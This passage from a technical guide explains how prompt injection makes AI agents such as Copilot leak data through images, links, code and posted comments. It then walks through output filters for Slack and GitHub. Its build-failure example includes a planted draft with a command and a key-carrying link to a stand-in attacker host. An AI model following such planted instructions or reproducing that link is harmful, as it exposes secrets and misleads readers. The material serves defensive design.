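In June 2026 the security company Varonis described an attack in which Copilot applied a suitable safeguard too late (*SearchLeak*, 2026). The attack began with a link to a genuine Microsoft address. The address of Copilot's search page for businesses can include a query, which Copilot treated as instructions as well as search terms. When a victim clicked the link, Copilot searched the victim's mailbox, took an email's subject line and wrote an HTML image tag with the subject line in the image's address. Subject lines can be valuable to a thief because some contain login codes.

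Microsoft guarded against dangerous HTML in Copilot's answers by wrapping the output in a code element, which makes a browser show a tag as text instead of acting on it. But Copilot added the code element only after it had finished generating the answer. Until then, the page displayed each part of the answer as it arrived and rendered any HTML in it. The browser therefore requested the image and sent the data before Copilot wrapped the image tag.

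A tester could find the fault only by recording the browser's network requests while the answer was still appearing, because the safeguard seemed to work judging by the finished answer.

The image request also had to go to a permitted domain, and again a Microsoft service relayed it. The list of permitted domains included Bing, whose search-by-image feature fetches a picture from any address it is given. Varonis put its own server's address, with the email title attached, inside a request to Bing. Bing was already on the list of image domains that Ravia published in 2025, so the fix for EchoLeak had left this route open for about a year.

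SearchLeak required one click on the original link and no further clicks after Copilot opened. Checking the domain before clicking would have helped little because it belonged to Microsoft. Only the victim saw the answer. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), its notice for CVE-2026-42824, records no exploitation and requires no action from customers. Microsoft rated the flaw critical but scored it only 6.5, partly because the victim had to take part in the attack.

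### Filtering an answer while it is being written

Varonis recommends cleaning AI output at the moment of rendering instead of afterward. More generally, a filter has to finish processing text before any renderer receives it.

The easiest way to follow this rule is to hold back the whole answer, filter it and then display it, but the user has to wait. A compromise is to show the incoming text as plain characters, with markup off, and apply the formatting once the filter has checked the complete answer. The user can start reading at once, and the browser has no image or link to act on.

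Filtering is harder when a product displays formatting during streaming. An image tag, like a password, can be split across two pieces, so the filter has to hold back any incomplete element. The Markdown format used in EchoLeak is harder to handle because the label can appear in the first paragraph and its address in the last. A filter that approves each piece separately can't tell that the label will become a link. The filter has to recheck the entire answer so far each time the display changes, and remove the link as soon as the address arrives.

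An agent that posts summaries to a team channel rarely needs any of this. Nobody is watching it write, so a delay of a few seconds hardly matters, and the posting program can wait for the complete text. But a developer who lets the agent post first and then edits or deletes bad messages repeats Microsoft's mistake, because a colleague's app may already have loaded an image.

### ReLeak, December 2026

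On December 3, 2026, the team that found EchoLeak, now called Cato AI Labs, disclosed the three ReLeak attacks on Copilot that Fadilpašić reported. As in EchoLeak, the attacker sent an email that the victim never had to open, and Copilot retrieved it while answering an ordinary request. The data left through an image address, through a link to a saved file or through code, according to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026). Microsoft patched the three routes on September 17, November 11 and November 15, and the researchers know of no real attacks.

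*An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) quotes the team as saying that "too little progress has been made". The team's employer sells protection for AI systems, so it has an interest in saying so. Still, Microsoft wrote in July 2025 that it also looks for variants when it repairs a reported leak, and outside researchers have kept finding variants since. In 2026, three years after the Bing Chat fix, an image address could still be used to send data out of Copilot.

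Data could also leak through the code Copilot runs. According to AIAIAI.FYI, Microsoft documented a block on outgoing traffic from the sandbox, the isolated environment where Copilot runs code, but the block failed. If code can contact an outside server while it runs, it can send data out before Copilot writes an answer, so filtering the answer won't stop the leak. The sandbox needs its own network limits, and they need to be tested.

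### From private answers to shared posts

EchoLeak, the Mermaid flaw and SearchLeak all involved private answers in a window that Microsoft controlled, so Microsoft could fix the renderer, as it did for Mermaid. A company whose agent posts to Slack or sends email usually can't fix the renderer, because other companies make the software that displays the message. Colleagues may read the same message in a desktop app, on a phone or in an email notification. A filter tested against one of these displays may miss something that another turns into an image or a link.

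PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* shows how a message created in one app can leak data when opened in another. Copilot Cowork, an agent that carries out tasks across Microsoft 365, could send its own user an email or Teams message without asking for approval. PromptArmor planted instructions that made it send a message containing external images whose addresses included download links to the user's files. Cowork's own window never showed the harmful part of the message, but when the user opened it in Teams, the images loaded and the attacker received the links. That message went only to the user. If an agent posted the same images to a channel, the first colleague to open the post could trigger the leak.

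Developers who can't control how a message is displayed can limit what they send. For the #support agent, the posting program could send the model's summary as plain text, with automatic link detection off and no images, and add any formatting itself. Readers would lose some convenience, such as clickable sources in the summary, but the various apps would have much less to interpret.

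## A Slack message filter that removes code blocks

A company that connects its own agent to Slack has to supply its own output filter. CNOE's *Slack Input/Output Guardrails* describes one for CAIPE, the project's open-source agent system. The CNOE project makes tools for teams that run companies' internal software platforms. CAIPE includes a Slack bot that answers employees' questions using smaller agents for services such as GitHub and the issue tracker Jira.

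### CNOE's outgoing checks

In the design, the bot checks an answer after CAIPE finishes it and before anything goes to Slack. Mentions, direct messages, alerts and retries all pass through one function in the bot's code, and CNOE puts the checks there so that they apply to every route.

| Check | Action on a match | What the user sees |
|---|---|---|
| Secrets and credentials | Replace the matching text | The answer with "[CREDENTIAL REDACTED]" in place of the secret |
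| Personal information | Replace the matching text | The answer with "[REDACTED]" in its place |
| Signs of made-up content | Add a disclaimer | The full answer, with a warning that some information could not be verified |
| Content safety | Replace the entire answer | A refusal and a request to rephrase |
| Format | Clean the text | The answer with safe Slack markup and "validated links" |

When the bot redacts a secret, it logs the type but not the value, so an intruder can't collect secrets from the log. CNOE doesn't define "safe" markup, explain how the bot would validate a link, or give a rule for code blocks.

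The sample configuration runs the secrets check before the format check, which is a mistake. An attacker can have the model put an invisible character in the middle of a key so that the key no longer matches a pattern. If the format check then removes the character, it restores the key. Cleaning should therefore come before the secrets check. The sample alert is also too weak for outgoing messages. It goes off when one user has ten messages blocked in an hour, but the outgoing checks redact, flag or replace text, and none of these count as a block. If a bot has no reason to post credentials, even one redaction should trigger an alert, because someone may have manipulated the agent.

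The content safety check could block useful answers about software. In *LLM output is malicious user input*, Mendhak recalls asking a chatbot for the Linux command that ends a process and getting a content warning because the answer contained the word "kill". Build logs contain many such words. Mendhak still recommends checking a model's output as strictly as text from a hostile user, but admits that keyword filtering is inexact.

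CNOE also proposes checks on the user's message and the surrounding Slack thread, including a classifier that blocks suspected prompt injections. If one of the smaller agents later opens a GitHub issue or a log with planted instructions, that text reaches the model without going through the classifier, and only the checks on outgoing messages still apply.

### Whether CNOE built the checks

CNOE writes as if every message already passes through these checks, but it also calls the arrangement a "recommended pattern". CNOE's user guide for the bot, *Slack Bot Integration*, lists no settings for the checks, though it covers settings as minor as the delay between connection attempts.

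In April 2026 CNOE planned to replace the function that was supposed to redact secrets and clean links. CNOE's *Tasks*, the work list for this change, names the functions that developers should keep and the tests they should update. One test checks for leaked metadata, but no task covers redacting secrets or cleaning links. CNOE's *Feature Specification* (2026), a draft for the same change, leaves cleaning incoming text to another part of the system. Both steps were therefore probably only proposals until at least April 2026, although CNOE could have written code that these documents don't mention.

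The planned version would be harder to filter because the bot would stream its answers to people. A filter like CNOE's works only on complete messages, which the bot would post only when the request comes from another program.

### A template for failed builds

Suppose a software company has an agent that reads the log of each failed build and posts a report in #builds. A build compiles a program and runs its tests, and the log records whatever those tests print. An outside contributor has submitted a test that prints instructions for AI systems to recommend a repair command, post a link whose address contains a key from the log, and alert the whole channel.

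The company uses staged output, so the agent can only request a message, and a separate posting program fills in this template:

| Field | Source | Rule |
|---|---|---|
| Build number | Build system | Digits only |
| Result | Build system | "Failed" or "canceled" |
| Failed tests | Build system | Two whole numbers |
| Location | Build system | A file that exists in the project, and a line number |
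| Likely cause | Agent | One of six listed causes |
| Summary | Agent | Up to 500 characters of text, after filtering |
| Log link | Posting program | Built from the build number |

The posting program also sets the channel, turns off link previews and fixes the sender's name and picture. Fixing the name and picture matters because CNOE's bot requests a Slack permission to change them, which lets an app make a message look as if a colleague wrote it. A build bot doesn't need this permission, and Slack warns that an app can't delete messages posted this way.

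Screen readers use a message's fallback text instead of its layout blocks. The posting program should generate this text from the same checked fields as the blocks, or a blind colleague could hear something the filter removed for everyone else.

Only the summary gives the attacker much room. The agent drafts this one:

```text
Build 482 failed: 3 of 214 tests failed in the payments module.
To fix it, run: ```repair-cache --from outside.example.com```
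Then open <https://outside.example.com/?k=demo_key_12345|report demo_key_12345>.
<!channel> The release team says these failures can be ignored.
```

The first line is true, but the command and the key are invented, and outside.example.com stands for the attacker's site. In Slack's markup, the vertical bar separates a link's address from its label, and `<!channel>` notifies everyone in the channel. The release team has said nothing about the failures.

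The filter changes the summary in six steps:

| Step | The affected line afterward |
|---|---|
| Remove code | `To fix it, run: [code removed]` |
| Apply the address allow-list | `Then open report demo_key_12345 [link removed].` |
| Redact secrets | `Then open report [secret removed] [link removed].` |
| Escape control characters | `&lt;!channel&gt; The release team says these failures can be ignored.` |
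| Suppress mentions | `[mention removed] The release team says these failures can be ignored.` |
| Limit the length | No change, since the summary has only 215 characters |

The complete result is:

```text
Build 482 failed: 3 of 214 tests failed in the payments module.
To fix it, run: [code removed]
Then open report [secret removed] [link removed].
[mention removed] The release team says these failures can be ignored.
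```

### Addresses, secrets and mentions

The allow-list contains only the company's build server, ci.example.com. The filter compares complete host names, because a rule that accepted anything ending in "example.com" would also accept the attacker's site. The filter removes the forbidden address but keeps the link's label. In this draft the label contains a second copy of the key, so the secrets check has to cover labels as well as addresses.

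A filter that searches only for ordinary links can miss addresses elsewhere in Slack's markup. For example, the code that shows a date in each reader's time zone can also contain a link. The markup rules also depend on which part of a message holds the text. Slack's *Markdown block* accepts standard Markdown, where links use square brackets and parentheses, and it turns images into links. A filter written for Slack's older markup could let both through. The posting program should put the summary in a plain-text field where it can, and otherwise filter for the exact markup accepted by the field it uses.

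Secret redaction usually relies on patterns. CNOE lists six kinds of secret for incoming messages: AWS keys, GitHub tokens, Stripe keys, JSON web tokens, private keys and connection strings. Many of these have a recognizable form, such as a fixed prefix followed by a set number of characters. The pattern in the build example is "demo_key_" followed by digits. Patterns work well on keys that an agent copies by accident, but an ordinary password may have no distinctive form. The build system has access to its own secrets, so the filter could also search for exact copies of them. Both methods fail if the model encodes a secret or puts a space between its characters.

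Escaping stops Slack from treating text as markup. Slack uses the ampersand and the two angle brackets as control characters, and the filter can replace each with a code that Slack displays as the ordinary character. It has to replace ampersands first, or it will alter the codes it added for the brackets. After escaping, readers would see `<!channel>` as text and nobody would be notified. The date code would also stop working, so escaping protects against some markup that the allow-list misses. It doesn't affect Markdown links, which need no angle brackets.

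The mention step is still useful because Slack can turn a plain "@channel" into a mention if the developer has switched on automatic parsing. The filter removes "@channel" and similar words in both their plain and escaped forms, along with mentions of single users and groups. The posting program should also leave automatic parsing off. Slack's `verbatim` setting controls this for text in layout blocks. The number of people notified depends on the word, from only the active members of a channel for "@here" to every member of the workspace except guests for "@everyone".

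Slack recommends at most 4,000 characters for a message's main text and cuts it off after 40,000. A build summary needs far less, and a limit of 500 characters leaves little space for an encoded file or a copied conversation. The filter should shorten long summaries between words, since a cut through an escape code would leave stray characters. But Slack generally lets an app post once a second in each channel, so an agent could spread a long leak over many short messages. The posting program should therefore accept only one summary per build.

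### The removal algorithm

The example filter removes code first, which is harder than it looks because Markdown has several ways to mark code. *CommonMark Spec* (MacFarlane, 2024) gives the most widely used definition of Markdown. A code block can start with a fence, which is a line of at least three backticks or three tildes, or it can consist of lines indented by four or more spaces. Inline code sits within a sentence, between matching runs of backticks.

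This pseudocode removes all of them:

```text
MARK = "[code removed]"

remove_code(text):
    repeat:
        old = text
        text = remove_fenced(text)
        text = remove_indented(text)
        text = remove_inline(text)
    until text == old
    return text

remove_fenced(text):
    fence = none
    for each line:
        if fence is none:
            if the line opens a fence:
                fence = its character and its length
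                output MARK
            else:
                output the line
        else if the line closes this fence:
            fence = none
        else:
            drop the line

remove_indented(text):
    find each group of lines indented by a tab or 4+ spaces
    that starts the text or follows a blank line or a MARK line
    replace the group with MARK

remove_inline(text):
    while the text contains a backtick:
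        n = length of the first run of backticks
        if a later run has exactly n backticks:
            replace both runs and all text between them with MARK
        else:
            replace everything from the first run onward with MARK
```

A fence closes only with a run of the same character at least as long as the opening one, so the program has to store the opening fence's character and length. If a model writes a block with a four-backtick fence and puts three backticks inside it, a simpler filter that deletes everything from one set of three backticks to the next would stop at the inner backticks and leave the rest of the block in the message. *Nested Code Fences in Markdown* shows the same technique for inline code, where two backticks on each side allow a single backtick in the text.

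A code block with no closing fence continues to the end of the document, according to *A problem with backtick code fences*, a discussion on the CommonMark forum. *code block utils.rs*, a file from a published programming library, treats unclosed blocks the same way. `remove_fenced` does too, without a special rule, because it drops every line until it finds a closing fence. A filter that deletes only complete blocks would leave an unclosed block in the message.

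The command in the build example has three backticks on each side but stays on one line. Slack displays it as a code block, but CommonMark classifies it as inline code because an opening backtick fence can't have more backticks later on the same line. The function `remove_inline` therefore removes it. If a run of backticks has no matching closing run, CommonMark treats it as ordinary text, but the function deletes the rest of the summary. One stray backtick can therefore remove a true sentence, which is a smaller problem than letting a command through.

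The loop repeats because deleting one piece of code can create another. For example, if a developer used an empty replacement instead of "[code removed]", deleting inline code at the start of a line could leave three tildes there, which would open a fence. The visible marker prevents this. The extra pass takes almost no time, and the loop always ends because each change removes some code and adds none.

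Slack's reference for its Markdown block lists backtick code but not tilde fences or indented code. The algorithm removes those too because colleagues and programs may copy a Slack message into an email or issue tracker, which may render the text differently. Slack's own display also changes, so a filter that matches its current documentation may be incomplete after the next update. Slack's *New supported markdown types for rich text in Block Kit* (2026) announces support for syntax-highlighted code, tables and task lists, while the Markdown block reference still lists all three as unsupported.

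Code can also get through when the filter and the renderer parse a message differently. If the filter treats an ordinary line as an opening fence, it will treat the real opening fence as the end of that block and leave the code after it in place, without its markers. Quotations and lists make such errors more likely, because a fence inside them can follow other symbols. For a summary of 500 characters, it is simpler and safer to reject the whole summary if it contains a backtick, three tildes in a row or an indented line. The full algorithm is more useful for longer messages, where rejecting the whole message would discard more text.

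### Deleting a block or only its markers

Some developers might prefer to unwrap a code block, deleting its backticks but keeping its contents. This preserves more information, but code formatting often makes text harmless, and unwrapping removes that protection. An address in the block could become a link with a preview. An "@channel" could become a mention if automatic parsing is on. A command could lose characters, because Slack treats pairs of asterisks or underscores as formatting and doesn't display them.

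Some evidence suggests that code formatting stops Slack previews. In *Stop unfurling of links in messages posted to Slack*, Jones asked users of the document tool Coda how to post links to Jira issues without previews. Another user put such a link between single backticks and found that no preview appeared. Rehberger's sample attack is consistent with this, since it told the model not to use a code block.

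But the Coda user looked only at the message, and nobody in the thread checked a server log to see whether Slack had requested the address anyway. The test also covered only inline code, not a code block. Slack's help article on missing previews lists six reasons why a preview might not appear, and code formatting isn't one of them. So removing the code formatting from an address may well turn on its preview, but leaving it in code doesn't reliably prevent a leak. The two preview settings remain the proper way to stop the request.

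In the same test, code formatting removed the link's preview but didn't turn the link into plain text. The Coda user reported that it still appeared as a link with its label, only in orange, although Slack's guide says that inline code uses no other formatting. A filter that skips code on the assumption that nothing inside it can be clicked would have missed the link.

Unwrapping is less dangerous if it happens before the other steps, because the allow-list can then remove an exposed address and the mention step can remove "@channel". But no later step detects harmful commands, so if the filter unwrapped the block in the build example, the bot would recommend the attacker's command in plain text. Deletion is the better default for a bot that reads text from strangers. GitHub instead leaves code in place, which makes more sense on a site where people come to discuss code.

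### What the filter leaves behind

The filtered build summary still contains its most harmful sentence, the claim that the release team has dismissed the failures. A colleague who believes it might ship a payments module that doesn't work. Every step correctly leaves the sentence alone because it has no link, code or secret. CNOE's check for made-up content might not help either. CNOE doesn't explain how the check would work, but if it compares an answer with the material the agent read, it would find support for the claim in the planted text.

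The model could also describe the key in words. "The key is demo, then key, then the first five numbers" doesn't match a pattern for "demo_key_12345", but a person could reconstruct the key from it. A longer secret would need a longer description, which is one reason to keep the character limit low. If #builds is open only to employees, the attacker may never see the sentence, but anyone in the channel can, including colleagues who have no right to the key. Because a manipulated model can reword a secret, pattern matching protects mainly against accidental leaks.

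Other agents may also read the summary. CNOE's bot ignores messages from other bots by default, but an administrator can let it respond to them in a channel, and this applies to all bots unless the administrator lists particular ones. In channels with another feature, which turns bots' alerts into Jira tickets, the false sentence could reappear in a ticket without its original context, where it would look like part of the company's own records.

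Removing the free-text summary would prevent all of this. The agent could still choose the wrong cause from the list of six, perhaps calling a real failure a network problem, but the number of failed tests would still be correct because it comes directly from the build system. A team that keeps the summary should show it separately from these fields and label it as the agent's own text, so that readers who notice the label don't mistake the summary for a record from the build system.

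### Stack traces and suggested fixes

A filter that deletes code also removes much of what makes a build report useful. When a program fails, it often prints a stack trace, which lists the functions that were running and where they are in the code. An experienced developer can sometimes find the fault from this list alone. A good agent might also suggest a one-line fix. Developers who see "[code removed]" instead may stop reading the reports or ask someone to turn the filter off.

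The posting program can replace the deleted code with a link to the full log, which only people with access to the project can open. They can still read the trace, but the program doesn't post it, or any secrets in the log, to everyone in #builds. Slack suggests uploading long text as a snippet, but a snippet shared in #builds would show the trace to the entire channel.

The log link can help the attacker if it appears in the wrong place. In the filtered summary, it would follow "To fix it, run:", and the planted command is in the log. The bot would be sending its readers to the attacker's instructions with a recommendation to follow them. It is safer to drop the whole summary whenever the filter finds code and to post only the other fields:

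```text
Build 482: failed
Failed tests: 3 of 214
Location: payments/refund.py, line 88
Likely cause: test failure
Summary withheld because it contained code.
Log: https://ci.example.com/builds/482
```

The build report no longer repeats the attacker's command under the bot's name, but a developer who opens the log will still see the planted paragraph. If the developer pastes the log into a coding agent, that agent will be exposed to the paragraph too. The log page should therefore mark test output as text from outside the company.

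The location field restores the most useful part of many stack traces. Ordinary code can take the file name and line number from the build system and check that the file exists, so a contributor can't use the field to insert a sentence. The location will sometimes be where the program stopped instead of where the original mistake is. The agent can suggest fixes as code changes through the team's normal review process, where colleagues can see exactly what would change and run the tests first. If the team regularly needs a few commands, such as one to rerun a build, the agent can choose from a fixed list and the posting program can supply the text.

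Whether to delete code blocks depends on who can write to the logs and who reads the channel. A link preview can send data out immediately, but a command in a Slack code block does nothing until a person or another agent runs it, so a team with limited time should turn off previews and restrict links first. A small group of developers whose builds include no outside code may reasonably keep stack traces if the other checks also examine the text inside them. A public project that builds strangers' code and reports to a large channel has a much stronger reason to delete them.

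## GitHub's checks on messages before they are posted

The code-hosting site GitHub uses staged output for agents that comment on projects hosted there. Its Agentic Workflows product can start an agent when something happens in a repository (a project's files and their history), such as a stranger opening an issue. The agent can read the issue and the code, but it can only request a comment. As in the build example, a separate program checks the request and posts the comment, but GitHub's program accepts long free text and usually leaves code in place.

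GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) lists "stage and vet all writes" as one of the product's four security principles. GitHub's *Security Architecture* assumes that an attacker may take over the agent and misuse the channels it is allowed to use, so the design doesn't depend on the model resisting planted instructions.

### How a request becomes a comment

Agentic Workflows run on GitHub Actions, a service that runs automated jobs. For example, an agent might read a user's crash report and suggest a cause. The agent runs in a job with read-only permission, so to post a comment, it calls a tool with the comment's text. The tool checks the request's format and saves the request to a file.

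When the agent finishes, its job uploads the file. A second job looks for threats, and a third, which has write permission, checks the request again and posts the comment. GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* (2026), published in May as version 1.21.0, allows requests to be passed only through these stored files, which provide a record and make tampering detectable. Each posting job should have only the permissions it needs.

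The repository's owner chooses which kinds of request to allow. If the owner chooses none, the agent can create only a single issue, according to GitHub's current reference page, *Safe Outputs*. Posts normally end with a footer that names the workflow and links to a record of the run, so readers can tell that an agent wrote the text. The owner can turn the footer off.

### The seven stages

The May specification sets out seven stages, in this order:

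| Stage | What the program examines | What happens if there is a problem |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Schema | Required fields and their types | It rejects the request |
| 2. Count limits | The number of requests of each type | It rejects all requests of that type |
| 3. Sanitizing | Titles, descriptions and comments | It changes the text, or rejects it if that isn't enough |
| 4. Domain filtering | Addresses in links and images | It replaces forbidden addresses |
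| 5. Target check | The repository that would receive the post | It rejects the request |
| 6. References | Placeholders for issues created in the same run | It rejects the request if it can't find the issue |
| 7. Final call | Nothing further; it posts the text | It reports an error |

A rejection at any of the first six stages prevents the final call. In the second stage, GitHub rejects every request of a type if the agent exceeds the limit for that type, because carrying out only some of them could leave work half finished. An attacker could therefore stop an agent from commenting by making it request two comments when the limit is one. This harm is fairly small, and accepting requests up to the limit would let the attacker's comment through if it came first.

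The target check limits the agent to its own repository unless the owner lists others. The specification requires exact names, but GitHub's reference also allows patterns and, for most request types, a setting that lets the agent pick any repository. Owners should avoid that setting if the agent can read private code, because the agent could copy that code into a public repository.

### How much a comment can hold

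By default, an agent can post one comment per run. The May specification limits a comment to 65,536 characters, 10 mentions and 50 links. If the agent exceeds a limit, the tool immediately reports the problem so the agent can correct its draft. The posting job checks the limits again in case someone has altered the file.

According to GitHub's reference, the limit is still 50 links, but owners can change it. The reference also lists a default maximum of 50 mentions per message, so it isn't clear whether the limit of 10 still applies.

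These limits are better at stopping spam than leaks. A single link can contain a key, and 65,536 characters is enough for a long configuration file. An agent that creates an issue can also attach up to 10 text files of 1 MB each. GitHub blocks attachments from folders where programs usually keep credentials, but that doesn't protect a password saved in an ordinary project file. On a public thread, the attacker can read the posted text, as in the GitLost attack described in the next section.

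The limits also apply to each run separately. If every new issue starts a run, an attacker who opens 100 issues could make the agent post 100 comments. An owner therefore needs to limit how often strangers can start the agent.

### What the sanitizer changes

The sanitizer first removes invisible characters, then removes addresses with unusual protocols and applies the domain list. It puts a backslash before a command such as "/close" at the start of the text, because a bot might obey it. It also deletes HTML comments, which readers don't see on the page but another agent might read in the source. Owners who need to store information for other programs can turn on a data field, which GitHub adds to the comment as a visible code block.

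GitHub's documentation is inconsistent about which addresses pass by default. In both the May specification and the October version of GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* (2026), the domain list starts empty, and an empty list means no filtering. According to the November reference, only secure addresses on GitHub's own domains pass unless the owner adds others. The reference is newer and written for users, so it is more likely to match the product, but an owner should set the list explicitly and test it. The same list controls which addresses the agent sees in incoming text, so adding a domain for outgoing messages also lets the agent see strangers' links to that domain.

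In GitHub's diagram of the system, secret redaction comes before sanitizing, as it does in CNOE's sample configuration. Redaction could therefore miss a key that contains invisible characters, and sanitizing could then restore the key by removing them. The threat-detection job runs between the two steps and might detect the key, but redacting secrets again after sanitizing would be more reliable.

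The sanitizer also puts backticks around mentions of people who are neither collaborators on the project nor already involved in the thread, so GitHub shows the name as code and notifies nobody. A separate rule covers phrases that trigger bots, such as "@copilot", but by default GitHub leaves the first 10 unchanged. The mention filter might catch some of these, but a single one may be enough to start another agent, so owners who don't need messages to trigger bots should set the limit to zero.

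### Why GitHub leaves code alone

In the May specification, GitHub forbids sanitizing code blocks and inline code. If the build agent from the previous section posted its draft as a GitHub comment, and the threat-detection job didn't stop it, the result would be roughly this:

| Part of the draft | After GitHub's checks |
|---|---|
| The planted repair command, in backticks | Unchanged |
| The link with a key in its address and label | The address disappears if its domain isn't allowed, but the label keeps the key unless redaction recognizes it |
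| A mention of an uninvolved stranger | In backticks, so the stranger gets no notification |
| The false claim that the failures can be ignored | Unchanged |

The Slack filter in the previous section would have deleted the command. GitHub has a good reason not to delete it, since a sanitizer can easily damage the code that people are discussing. In several programming languages, for example, the @ sign has a meaning unrelated to mentioning a person. A reviewer may also want to correct an address in a configuration file.

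A filter's changes to code are especially risky in a suggestion block, a code block whose contents a developer can add to the project with a click. If the filter replaces an address there with "(redacted)", the developer may add that word to the project. The sanitizer has damaged a documentation link in a suggestion block this way.

Code formatting makes some text, such as mentions, harmless on GitHub itself, but developers and coding agents may still run a command planted in a code block. Anyone can read a password in a code block on a public thread. GitHub also turns code blocks marked as Mermaid into diagrams, and the May rule makes no exception for them.

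The exemption also makes the parsing mismatches described in the previous section more dangerous. Suppose a line has four spaces followed by three backticks. Under the CommonMark rules, this line can be a short piece of indented code, with ordinary text after it. A sanitizer might mistake the backticks for the start of a code block and skip everything that follows, so readers would get working links that had not been checked. A filter that deletes code would be safer, because making the same mistake would delete the text after the backticks. There is no evidence that GitHub's sanitizer makes this mistake.

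### The November change to addresses in code

By November 2026, GitHub's reference was no longer consistent with exempting all code from filtering. According to a passage about files attached to issues, the program always filters addresses in HTML files, even inside backticks and even if the workflow "allows URLs in Markdown code regions". This implies that owners can choose whether to allow addresses in Markdown code, and the wording suggests that the program filters them by default.

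The reference doesn't name this setting or give its default, so an owner can't rely on either behavior without testing it. To test it, the owner can have the agent post a message to a private repository with the same unlisted address in a sentence, in inline code and in a code block. If the address remains only in the code, the exemption still applies.

Filtering addresses in code is a reasonable compromise, because it stops a reader from copying the attacker's address while leaving most of the code intact. It doesn't stop a harmful command that contains no address. It can also break a legitimate code suggestion, so an owner may want to allow addresses for an agent that reviews trusted colleagues' code and filter them for one that answers strangers.

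### When backticks decide what happens

A phrase can trigger an action on GitHub even if it contains no link or mention. If someone merges a pull request (a proposed code change) whose description contains "Closes #123", GitHub closes issue 123. If the phrase is in backticks, the issue stays open.

Putting backticks around a phrase such as "fixes #123" stops it from closing the issue. Agents sometimes add these backticks to their messages, so GitHub offers an option, `normalize-closing-keywords`, that removes them and lets the phrase take effect. When GitHub prepares text for an agent to read, it adds backticks to such phrases.

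This is another reason to be careful about unwrapping code. An agent might use backticks because it is quoting a stranger, and removing them could turn the quotation into a command to close an unrelated issue. GitHub's option is narrower than general unwrapping because it affects only recognized closing phrases, but leaving it off is still safer for an agent that quotes outsiders. If the workflow needs to close issues, ordinary code can write the closing phrase with an issue number it has already checked.

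### The threat-detection job

Before the posting job starts, a second model checks the agent's requests. According to GitHub's *Threat Detection*, it checks for signs of prompt injection, leaked secrets and malicious code changes, marks each as true or false, and lists its reasons. By default, a single "true" blocks everything the agent has requested. GitHub also blocks the requests if the check crashes, so an attacker can't bypass the check by crashing it.

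This model has no write permission, so an attacker who manipulates it can't use it to post anything. It receives the requests, any code changes and the workflow's original prompt, but not the live repository. It might detect a password or a suspicious command, but it has no good way to check whether the release team really dismissed a failed test.

By default, the job uses the same AI engine as the agent, though with different instructions, so text that deceives the agent may well deceive the job too. Owners can choose a different engine or add conventional tools, such as a secret scanner. These tools are worth adding because they are less likely to make the same mistakes as the model.

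The extra checks need testing too. GitHub's guide includes sample code for Llama Guard, a model that labels text "safe" or "unsafe". The sample approves any answer that contains the word "safe". Since "unsafe" contains "safe", it would also approve text that Llama Guard had labeled unsafe. The check would appear to work to an owner who copied the sample, but a test with one harmful message would reveal the mistake.

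### What happens to flagged requests

In May 2026 GitHub added rules for a "warn mode", in which a flagged request doesn't always stop. The result depends on the type of request:

| Class | Examples | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Reviewable | Comments, new issues, pull requests | GitHub posts the text with a caution and the label "agentic threat detected" |
| Convertible | Adding code to an existing pull request | GitHub opens a new pull request with the same warning |
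| Abort | Adding labels, closing issues, merging code, starting other workflows | GitHub refuses the request and reports an error |

The classes make sense for code changes, since a person can inspect a new pull request before merging it. The warning also gives readers a reason to doubt a false statement. But it doesn't contain a leak, because an attacker can still read a public comment.

A better policy would depend on the reason for the flag as well as the type of request. The detection model already reports leaked secrets separately, so the posting job could refuse every message flagged for a secret and use warnings only for other problems. Until GitHub offers this, owners of public repositories should keep the blocking behavior for comments.

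A person can also release requests that the threat check has blocked. With a GitHub maintenance tool, they can repeat the posting step from an earlier run that was blocked, cancelled or stopped by a network error. Only people with high-level access to the repository can use it. The tool is useful when the check has blocked a harmless message, but users should read the reason for the failure first. Someone who assumes it was a network error could publish a message that the check had correctly stopped.

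### Preview mode and human approval

GitHub's "staged mode" lets an owner preview what an agent would post. It is separate from the staged-output design, which is always in use. With `staged: true`, the program skips every write and puts the full text of each request in the run's summary. Owners can preview everything or only some types of output, such as new issues, while letting comments through. The mode is off by default, and GitHub recommends it for testing new workflows.

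An agent that behaves well in a few previews may still misbehave when an attacker writes to it later. An owner should also test it with hostile issues and invented secrets, and look at what it tries to post. A private repository is best for this, because outsiders can read the run's logs on a public project, and a preview there could expose the private text it was supposed to catch.

Preview mode also has no button for posting the text a person has just read, so it doesn't work as an approval step. Owners who want approval can attach the posting job to a protected environment, a GitHub feature that can require a named reviewer's approval before a job runs. GitHub argues in the specification that manual approval creates bottlenecks and defeats the purpose of automation. That is fair for an agent that labels hundreds of issues a day, but the delay seems worth accepting for one that reads private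 code and posts in public a few times a week.

A cautious owner could start with settings like these, all of which appear in GitHub's reference:

```yaml
safe-outputs:
  staged: true
  allowed-domains: [ci.example.com]
  mentions: false
  max-bot-mentions: 0
  add-comment:
    max: 1
    max-links: 3
```

After testing, the owner would change `staged` to false. The other settings would still limit the agent to one comment with at most three links and prevent it from notifying people or starting bots.

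### The risks GitHub says remain

GitHub acknowledges in the specification that an agent may still write "legitimate-seeming but contextually inappropriate content" within its limits, such as the false claim about the failed tests. GitHub addresses this with monitoring and periodic review, which can catch a pattern of bad comments but may not catch the first one before someone believes it.

GitHub also accepts that secrets may get through if they have an unfamiliar format or the agent disguises them. It rates its protection as high for secrets that the owner has registered and medium for those it has to recognize by pattern, but these are its own judgments, and the specification includes no test results to support them. Keeping secrets out of the agent's reach, another of GitHub's four principles, is safer.

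Other risks come from how owners set up their projects. A repository list may be too broad, or an attacker who gains control of the repository may rewrite the workflow. In the October version, GitHub also listed the risk that private data could reach a public repository or log if an owner turns off a default protection. A strict setting prevents owners from turning the protection off, but without that setting they get only a warning.

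To reduce the amount of hostile text an agent reads, GitHub also offers integrity filtering, which limits what the agent sees based on who wrote it and whether someone trusted has vetted it. *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering*, from the company's research group, GitHub Next, contrasts this with content filtering, which it describes as a "cat-and-mouse game" in which attackers keep rewording their instructions. Integrity filtering could protect an agent that summarizes discussions among maintainers. An agent that answers strangers' bug reports still has to read them, so it depends much more on the checks on what it posts.

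## Private text in public GitHub comments, 2026

An agent that comments on a public GitHub thread can leak data just by including it in the comment, with no link, image or outside server. In 2026, one group of researchers showed an agent publishing text from a private repository this way, and another showed agents from three companies publishing credentials.

### GitLost

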